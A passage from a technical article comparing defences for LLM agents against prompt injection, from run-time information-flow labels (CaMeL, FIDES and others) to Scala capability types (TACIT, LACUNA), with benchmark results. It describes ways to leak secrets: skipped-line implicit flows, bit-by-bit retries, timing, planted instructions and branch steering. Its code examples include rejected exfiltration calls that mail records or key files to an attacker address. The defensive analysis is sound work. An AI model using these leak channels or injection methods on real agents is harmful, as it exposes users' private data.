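If the card number is odd, the program sets `tmp` to false and the interpreter marks it as secret. The program then skips the line `odd = False`, so `odd` stays true and keeps its public label. The email goes out because its condition appears public. If the card number is even, `tmp` stays true, the program sets `odd` to false, and no email goes out. The stranger again learns whether the number is odd.

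The interpreter changes labels only on lines that run, but in this example the skipped line carries the information. A known remedy is to stop the program when it tries to change a public variable inside a block that depends on a secret. Here, the program would stop at `tmp = False`. This rule would also stop some harmless programs.

Stopping a program can also leak information. When a CaMeL program fails, a loop outside the interpreter asks the privileged model for another attempt, and the labels start afresh. Garby and colleagues point out that a program could fail repeatedly to leak a secret one bit at a time. A 16-digit card number would take about 53 attempts. CaMeL censors the error messages, but this offers no formal guarantee. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to several cooperating agents, inherits both this leak and the one through skipped lines.

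Python makes such gaps harder to close. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes this to Python's dynamic types, use of exceptions for control flow, and introspection. The paper recommends a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditions.

Timing can also carry information. CaMeL's interpreter gives programs no clock, so they can't measure delays, but a stranger who receives two permitted emails can still measure the time between them.

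### What a policy can't judge

Labels don't show whether a text is true. A malicious ticket might make the quarantined model falsely report that the company has already resolved a complaint. The employee is allowed to read that summary, so no policy blocks it, and the customer never gets an answer. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) gives a similar example in which an agent emails a day's schedule to the user's boss. A malicious calendar entry can't change the recipient, but it can corrupt the message.

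A case of this kind appears in AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants hidden instructions in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. A user asks for hotel A, and a planted review recommends hotel B. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), whose system protects classified data at compile time, reports that the agent booked hotel A but quoted the review to the user. The benchmark counted this as a successful attack because it searched the answer for hotel B's name. The user was allowed to read the review, so the system had enforced its policy correctly.

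Someone also has to write the policies and keep them up to date. This worries Willison because he still struggles with Amazon's cloud permission settings after two decades in application security. Policies that are too strict lead to so many approval requests that people stop reading them.

CaMeL's policies also apply to one call at a time. Nikolaou and colleagues give an example of a rule that such policies can't express, in which a security team wants every incident ticket to be resolved or escalated before the agent finishes. Their system, CaMeLoT, turns the privileged model's program into a diagram of possible steps and checks rules about their order before anything runs. If a program could isolate a computer without the required approval, CaMeLoT reports the offending path so that the model can repair the program. It assumes a loop may repeat any number of times, so it can reject safe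 programs. The support company would still need a running total for refunds, because a thousand refunds can all have acceptable labels.

### Labels that spread

Labels can spread until an agent can do very little. This happens quickly in an agent that makes ordinary tool calls, because every result enters the model's context. After the model reads one untrusted ticket, the ticket could influence anything it writes, so every later call has to inherit the ticket's label.

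A program can keep values in separate variables, so a label spreads only to values that depend on the labelled one. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) explains that this precision is hard to achieve without a program because traditional tracking follows data through predictable operations, while a language model may paraphrase a text, translate it or use it to choose its next action. The paper's system, NeuroTaint, looks for such influence after the agent has finished, so it can help investigators but can't block a call. Writing code removes the pauses between calls but makes it easier to tell which data affects each one.

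Microsoft's FIDES brings some of this precision to agents that make ordinary tool calls. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how FIDES hides untrusted results in variables. The planning model can pass a variable to a tool, ask a quarantined model about it, or read it directly. Reading it directly makes the planning model's context untrusted, and FIDES then blocks consequential actions such as payments.

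FIDES requires consequential actions to come from a trusted context and lets data go only to people who are allowed to read it. It doesn't track implicit flows. Costa and colleagues considered full protection too restrictive, because an agent that had used a tool for reading secrets could then use almost no tools with publicly visible effects.

They tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent fell for 152 attacks and FIDES without its policies for 21, after the researchers had removed cases that the benchmark misjudged. With policies, none succeeded. The percentage of tasks completed without an attack shows the cost:

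| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no policies | Ordinary agent with labels and policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75% | 37% | 59% |
| Travel | 70% | 73% | 41% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20% | 47.6% |

Hiding data in variables recovered much of the lost work in three of the four groups. In the travel group, the policies hardly restricted the ordinary agent, and GPT-4o had trouble using the variables. Using OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason at length, raised FIDES's result there from 41 to 68 percent.

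### When the plan depends on the data

An agent can't fully plan some tasks in advance. If a user asks it to do everything on today's to-do list, the model has to read the list to find out which tools it needs. Costa and colleagues classified about 43 percent of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks as dependent on data in this way, compared with 5 percent of office tasks and 10 percent of travel tasks.

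A CaMeL program can include branches for cases the model expects, and the data determines which one runs. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* calls this branch steering when the data is untrusted. In one run of CaMeL without policies, the model was asked to follow the instructions in a file and wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose the agent's actions.

FIDES can limit how much information reaches the planning model. To check whether an email requests a meeting, it can restrict the quarantined model's output to yes or no, which conveys at most one bit. A policy may let that answer influence the plan, because an attacker can hardly fit an instruction into one bit. Costa and colleagues didn't use these restricted answers in their AgentDojo tests. The support company should be careful with them, because the answer to "Does this customer deserve a refund?" is also one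 bit, and a false yes could cost 50 dollars.

A person can also vouch for the data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes PRUDENTIA, a system built on FIDES. PRUDENTIA gives the planning model the labels and policies, and lets it ask the user to endorse untrusted data, which makes the data trusted. If an email contains ten tasks, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls.

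On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini, PRUDENTIA completed 59.1 percent of tasks without asking anyone, compared with 50.1 percent for FIDES and 24.3 percent for an agent that needed approval for every consequential action. With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed about half as many human decisions as FIDES across the tasks each completed, but it completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2 percent compared with 75.7 percent).

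On WASP, a benchmark for agents that use websites, PRUDENTIA blocked every attack and needed no approvals. The agents only had to post a comment or upvote a post, so they never needed to read untrusted text. Kolluri and colleagues assume that people make the right decisions. A user who endorses an email without noticing a hidden instruction approves everything the agent does because of that instruction.

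### How much work still gets done?

Estimates of the share of tasks CaMeL completes vary widely. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) cites 77 percent. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran CaMeL through an adapter on all of AgentDojo and reports that it stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, or about 30 percent. SecureClaw, the paper's own system, completed 59. The adapter and the choice of model may account for part of the gap between the two CaMeL figures, so neither reliably predicts how much CaMeL would reduce task completion at a particular company.

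Garby and colleagues provide a more informative comparison, because they ran CaMeL with and without its policies. They also tested their own agent, Randori, on the same 16 banking tasks. For the two models that they used with both systems, the results were:

| System | Tasks completed with GPT-5.2 | Tasks completed with MiMo-v2.5 | Successful attacks, both models |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies | 67% | 71% | 5 of 622 |
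| CaMeL with policies | 37.5% | 37.5% | 0 of 588 |
| Randori, with policies | 75% | 65% | 2 of 864 |

Each task was run only three times, so small differences between the completion rates mean little. But CaMeL clearly completed far fewer tasks with policies than without them.

CaMeL resisted nearly all the attacks even without policies. In about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a tool that the plan would never call. So planning before reading is a strong defence by itself, and on this benchmark the policies added little security given their drawbacks. They would probably matter more against an attacker who knew the plan and only tried to change an address, as in the example with Bob.

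Randori completed more tasks partly because its planning model can endorse particular data in the program before the agent reads anything. When Garby and colleagues removed this option, completion fell from 75 to 62.5 percent with a third model, Qwen3.7-plus, and from 65 to 54 percent with MiMo-v2.5. Randori also tests its program on simulated data until it works, so it doesn't need CaMeL's retries on real data, which can leak information.

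The researchers used the proof assistant Lean to prove that Randori's interpreter prevents secret data from affecting public results, except by influencing whether a program finishes. They also proved that endorsing untrusted data doesn't weaken this protection. But endorsement can still lead to a wrong payment. Both successful attacks involved the same task, in which the user told the agent to pay a bill described in a file whose contents the attacker had replaced. Without endorsement, the interpreter blocked the payment.

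The support company's program could endorse only the topic of each ticket, and only when choosing who gets 10 dollars for a late delivery, without changing who may read any customer record. A customer who lies about a delivery might then get 10 dollars, but not another customer's record.

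## Can a compiler prove what a program may do before it runs?

CaMeL's interpreter checks each call as the program reaches it. If a program refunds thirty customers and then tries to email a record to a stranger, the interpreter blocks the email, but the refunds have already gone out. A compiler could reject the whole program before the first refund if types recorded which bindings each piece of code may use. Ordinary types don't record this. In TypeScript, a function that shortens a customer's record can have the same type as one that also emails the record to a stranger.

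The programming language Scala has an experimental feature called capture checking, which tracks capabilities in types. *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) proposes that agents write Scala programs instead of calling tools directly. The paper's system, TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), runs a program only if it compiles.

### Capabilities in types

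In Scala, a capability is an ordinary object that gives access to something, such as a file or a mail server, much like the references in Miller's model. Capture checking adds a capture set to a value's type, which lists the capabilities the value might use:

```scala
String -> String          // uses no capabilities
String ->{mail} String    // may use mail
String => String          // may use any capability
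```

A function with an empty capture set is pure. It can compute a result from its argument, but it can't send, save or print anything. The compiler works out the set from the code, so a function that calls `mail.send` has `mail` in its set even if it makes that call only under certain conditions.

A function can go wherever the program expects its own capture set or a larger one, but not where the program expects a smaller one. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, illustrate this with a function that accepts only tasks that use the network. A version for the support company could accept only tasks that use mail:

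```scala
def sendUpdate(job: () ->{mail} Unit) = job()
sendUpdate(() => mail.send("ana@shop.example", fs.read("keys.txt")))   // rejected
```

`()` means that the task takes no arguments, and `Unit` means that it returns nothing useful. The surrounding program can use both `mail` and `fs`, the file system, but this task may use only `mail`, so the compiler rejects the second line. A schema for `mail.send` couldn't express that rule, because it would accept the text of a secret file like any other text.

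### A wrapper for secrets

TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`. In simplified form:

```scala
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` and `U` stand for any types. The agent's program can't take the data out of the wrapper. It can only pass a function to `map`, which applies the function to the data and wraps the result again. The single arrow in `T -> U` means the function must be pure.

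Suppose the support company's `customers.get` returned wrapped records:

```scala
val record: Classified[String] = customers.get("C-88")

record.map(r => r.take(200))                              // accepted
record.map(r => mail.send("thief@attacker.example", r))   // rejected
```

The accepted line keeps the first 200 characters of the record. In the rejected line, the function has the type `String ->{mail} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The compiler reports that `mail` can't flow into the empty capture set, and TACIT returns the error to the model so the model can correct the program. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, a longer version of the TACIT paper, includes similar errors from real runs, one of them from an agent that tried to print a GitHub key.

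The wrapper also stops a program from revealing whether a card number is odd by either emailing "Hello" or sending nothing. Outside `map`, the result of the odd-number test is wrapped, and an `if` doesn't accept a wrapped value. Inside `map`, the program can test the number but can't call `mail.send`. The skipped-line trick that CaMeL's strict mode missed also fails, because the compiler tracks changes to variables and doesn't let a pure function change one outside itself. Errors are harder to rule out in advance, since almost any program can divide by zero or run out of memory, so TACIT catches them at run time and can wrap them like other results.

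The agent can still work with secrets. The `chat` function sends wrapped text to a trusted model, perhaps one on the company's own computers, and returns a wrapped answer. If the program prints a wrapped summary, the user sees the text through a separate channel, while the model that wrote the program receives only `Classified(****)`. The summary stays wrapped in later turns, so the user can ask a follow-up question about it without exposing it to that model.

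### File access that ends with its block

TACIT also uses capture checking to limit how long a program can use a capability. A program requests access to a folder for one block of code:

```scala
val may = requestFileSystem("/reports") { fs =>
  fs.access("/reports/may.txt").read()          // accepted
}

val june = requestFileSystem("/reports") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("/reports/june.txt").read()   // rejected
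}
```

The first block returns plain text. The second returns a function that would read the file later, so the function's type must include `fs`. But `fs` exists only inside the block, so the compiler rejects any result whose type includes it.

The same rule covers objects the program gets through `fs`. In one real run, an agent tried to return a list of file handles, and the compiler rejected the code because each handle still gave access to the file system. A caretaker, by contrast, left a ticket's `reply` function working after revocation.

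The compiler can't determine whether a path the program builds as it runs will be inside `/reports`, so TACIT's library checks each path at run time. The library also checks commands and servers at run time.

The program also chooses which folder to request, so the operator has to limit the choice. According to Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's documentation, programs can by default request only folders inside the server's working directory. The equivalent network limit is optional, and if the operator doesn't set it, the only list of approved servers is the one the program supplies. TACIT also lets a program post wrapped data to an approved server. As documented, a program could therefore approve a stranger's server and post a secret to it without breaking any type rule. An operator can prevent this by setting the network limit, but the default seems dangerous.

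### What safe mode forbids

Scala has features that would let a program hide its capabilities from the compiler. TACIT requires agents to use a subset of the language called safe mode, which forbids:

- type casts and pattern matches that the compiler can't verify
- the `caps.unsafe` module, which offers ways around capture checking
- `@unchecked` annotations, which silence some of the compiler's checks
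- reflection, which lets a program find and use parts of itself by name as it runs
- global objects and functions that don't follow the safety rules themselves

Safe mode also turns on capture checking and makes the compiler track which values may be missing. A cast like TypeScript's `as any` would stop the program from compiling.

According to a version of lampepfl's *TACIT* documentation from about March 2026, TACIT used a separate validator to search the agent's code for forbidden patterns and had not yet moved to the Scala compiler's safe mode. Such a validator has the same basic weakness as the name filters for Python. The later documentation keeps the validator but lists the compiler's safe mode as on by default.

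### Testing the wrapper

The researchers gave an agent a small software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and a database. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 hidden instructions, which made 120 trials. In 11 more trials the user asked for the secrets, five times openly and six times under a pretext, such as an emergency that required new passwords. Each model ran all 131 trials with the wrapper and again without it. A trial counted as safe if no secret appeared in the agent's output:

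| Model and trials | Safe with the wrapper | Safe without it |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, hidden instructions (120) | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, requests for secrets (11) | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, all trials (131) | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, hidden instructions (120) | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, requests for secrets (11) | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, all trials (131) | 100% | 91.6% |

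Without the wrapper, Sonnet resisted every hidden instruction but granted two of the 11 requests for secrets, so its improvement comes only from those requests. MiniMax granted eight of the 11 and also followed three hidden instructions. The perfect scores with the wrapper are expected if the compiler works, since it rejects these leaks regardless of what code the model writes. They are good evidence that the implementation works, but the researchers built the test around the kind of leak that the wrapper prevents.

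The wrapper didn't reduce the models' success on ordinary tasks. Sonnet completed 99.2 percent of the 120 ordinary trials with the wrapper and 83.3 percent without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0 percent with it and 88.3 percent without it. The researchers suspect that Sonnet's lower figure without the wrapper is an artefact of their setup, because the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

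They also moved AgentDojo's four groups of tasks to TACIT and ran them with two models. Only one of 1,926 attacks counted as successful, the hotel review that the agent quoted to its user. Capture checking may have contributed little to this result. The functions that read emails, files, messages and reviews returned wrapped text, so the model that wrote the programs generally didn't see the hidden instructions, as in Willison's dual LLM pattern. The published types of the functions that send money or email include no capability, and the model's instructions cover side effects inside `map`, so the compiler seems not to have enforced purity for those actions.

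*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* describes TACIT's task completion rate as comparable to CaMeL's, but individual results vary a lot. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9 percent of the office tasks, compared with a published 81.4 percent for CaMeL. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3 percent of the travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1.4 percent.

### Can models write such programs?

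The researchers tested whether models can write Scala with capture checking, which is rare in training data. On τ²-bench, in which an agent serves simulated customers of an airline and a shop, three models solved between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points more tasks with Scala programs than with ordinary tool calls. The researchers attribute the improvement to the exact result types and the compiler's error messages. Rai similarly found that models write better scripts when they know what a tool returns, which suggests that a simpler typed language might bring much of this benefit.

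On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software problems from GitHub, MiniMax solved 41.7 percent through TACIT and 43.3 percent with ordinary tools, a difference of five problems. The researchers think solving these problems relies more on shell commands, which are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

Compiler errors caused little delay. In the customer-service tests, between 0.3 and 7.9 percent of programs needed a second attempt, depending on the model and the task, and those programs needed 1.1 to 1.4 retries on average. Compiling a program took less than a second.

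### Code that fills a gap

Several of the same researchers went further in May 2026. In Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, a developer writes a program and leaves gaps for the model to fill while the program runs. For the support company, such a program might contain this function:

```scala
def compensate(late: List[Ticket], refunds: Refunds^): Int =
  agent[Int]("Refund $10 for each late delivery. Return the number.")
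```

The `^` marks `refunds` as a capability that the compiler tracks. When the program reaches `agent`, the following happens:

1. LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type of the result (a whole number), the surrounding code and a list of the names available there.
2. The model writes Scala code to fill the gap.
3. The compiler checks the code as if a developer had typed it at that point.
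4. If the code passes, it runs, and its result takes the place of the `agent` call. Otherwise, LACUNA sends the errors to the model, which tries again.

With capture checking on, generated code can use only the capabilities in scope at the gap it fills. It can issue refunds because `refunds` is in scope, but it can't send mail unless a mail capability is also in scope, even if a hidden instruction tells the model to send it. A developer can therefore grant authority for one step of a task by choosing a function's parameters, without a separate policy file. But the scope also includes definitions at the top of the file, so a mail object defined there is available to every gap below it.

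The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole before any of it runs. If the model's code would issue thirty refunds and then return text instead of a number, the compiler rejects it and none of the refunds happen. This prevents type errors from interrupting the refunds partway through, but the payment service could still fail after the tenth refund.

LACUNA also makes the wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the model has to write the function passed to `map` without seeing the secret data. In LACUNA, that function can contain another gap, which a trusted local model fills after reading the data. The compiler still requires the new code to be pure.

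Zhao and colleagues ran about 400 tests of the compiler. Each test filled a gap in a program with correct or faulty code, and all gave the expected result. They also tried LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 hard research questions. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash, it answered 27.1 percent correctly, and the compiler rejected 8.6 percent of the generated code. Without an ordinary agent for comparison, it's hard to tell whether 27.1 percent is good.

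On 392 customer-service tasks from τ²-bench, the same model solved 76.0 percent with LACUNA and 90.0 percent with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par", which is hard to accept for a gap of 14 points. With the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the figures were 29.1 and 33.2 percent, and the compiler rejected 89 percent of its code on telecom tasks. The types probably aren't the main cause of the gap, since TACIT did slightly better than tool calls on the same benchmark. But TACIT's tests used other models, and LACUNA also replaces the loop that normally runs an agent, so the two results aren't directly comparable.

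Eight of 1,898 AgentDojo attacks succeeded against LACUNA, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues explain that the compiler doesn't stop an attacker from steering the model into misusing a capability the task needs.

### What the compiler can't check

TACIT's guarantee depends on components that the compiler doesn't prove correct: the compiler itself, the system that runs the compiled program, the trusted local model and a library of roughly 1,000 lines. Developers can also exempt part of a library from the rules of safe mode by marking it `@assumeSafe`, and a mistake in that part could undo the protection.

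Pham and colleagues used the proof assistant Lean to prove that the rules of capture checking are sound in a small model of the language. The proof doesn't cover the full Scala compiler, and nobody had yet proved that safe mode provides all the guarantees claimed for it.

The rules for capture checking are still changing. Scala's `Try` runs a piece of code and stores either its result or its error. Earlier capture checking treated the stored value as pure, but a program that opens it later can throw the error again, which requires a capability. Pham and colleagues corrected this by adding categories of capabilities, so that `Try` keeps only those that affect control flow. Categories could also help agents. For example, the support company could define one for payments and accept any function that uses no capabilities in it.

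Capture checking also doesn't cover several kinds of harm:

- **Timing:** A pure function can run longer when a card number is odd, and anyone who can measure the delay learns one bit.
- **Outside commands:** If a program may start `git`, the new process runs outside Scala, where capture checking doesn't apply. Deno's permission flags have the same weakness.
- **Other tools:** An agent that still has its usual shell can ignore TACIT altogether, so the documentation recommends turning off the built-in tools.
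- **Overwriting:** The wrapper keeps a program from revealing a secret file but not from replacing its contents. By default, an agent could overwrite the list of SSH keys that may log in to the computer.
- **Endless loops:** TACIT has an optional time limit, but a loop that only computes can continue in the background after the limit expires.

A program can also misuse capabilities it is allowed to have. In the `compensate` function, the generated code could refund an order that isn't in `late`, because an order number is plain text. Zhao and colleagues suggest that future types could include properties such as a number's range, which would let the compiler check the 50-dollar limit on each amount but wouldn't limit the total.

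Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* calls tracked capabilities "the most important new feature of Scala", but the project still classes them as experimental. TACIT is built with Scala's nightly versions, which can change from one day to the next. A company that adopted TACIT now would have to expect programs that compile today to fail after an update.

### Proofs compared with labels

CaMeL attaches labels to data while a program runs, whereas TACIT checks what code may do with data before the program starts. The compiler's main advantages are that it rejects leaks before the program runs and covers every path through the code, including those a particular run would skip. TACIT also lets agents write their own functions, which CaMeL's restricted Python doesn't allow.

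Labels can make finer distinctions because they are checked at run time, when the real values are known. When customer C-88 asks for her record, CaMeL can compare the recipient's address with the record's permitted readers and allow the email. `Classified` has no list of readers, so a program can't mail the record to anyone. To support this request, the company would have to add a trusted function that takes a customer number, looks up the address in the host and sends the record there. This is probably safer than letting the program supply an address, but someone has to write such a function for every legitimate use of a secret.

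Unlike the wrapper, labels can also record whether data is trustworthy. If the support agent reads unwrapped tickets and holds the refund capability, an instruction hidden in one can still make it refund every open order. TACIT assumes such text may influence the model and limits only what the resulting code can reach. In CaMeL, the planning model writes the program before any ticket reaches it.

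*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* argues that labels have a gap that types avoid, because labels are lost once data enters a model's context as ordinary language. This claim is too broad. The danger is real in a system that treats whatever the model writes next as unlabelled, and CaMeL comes close to this when a program fails and the planning model starts again with fresh labels. But CaMeL's planning model normally never sees the tools' results, and FIDES marks the whole context as untrusted once the model has read something untrusted, so the label spreads too far instead of disappearing. TACIT avoids the problem in much the same way as CaMeL, by keeping secret text out of the model's context, but it can do this only for data that someone has wrapped.

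The researchers regard the two methods as complementary and suggest adding run-time rules, such as rate limits and audit logs, to the functions in TACIT's library. The support company could have the compiler reject programs that might leak a record, then have the host check each refund's amount, count the refunds and confirm that each order was late.
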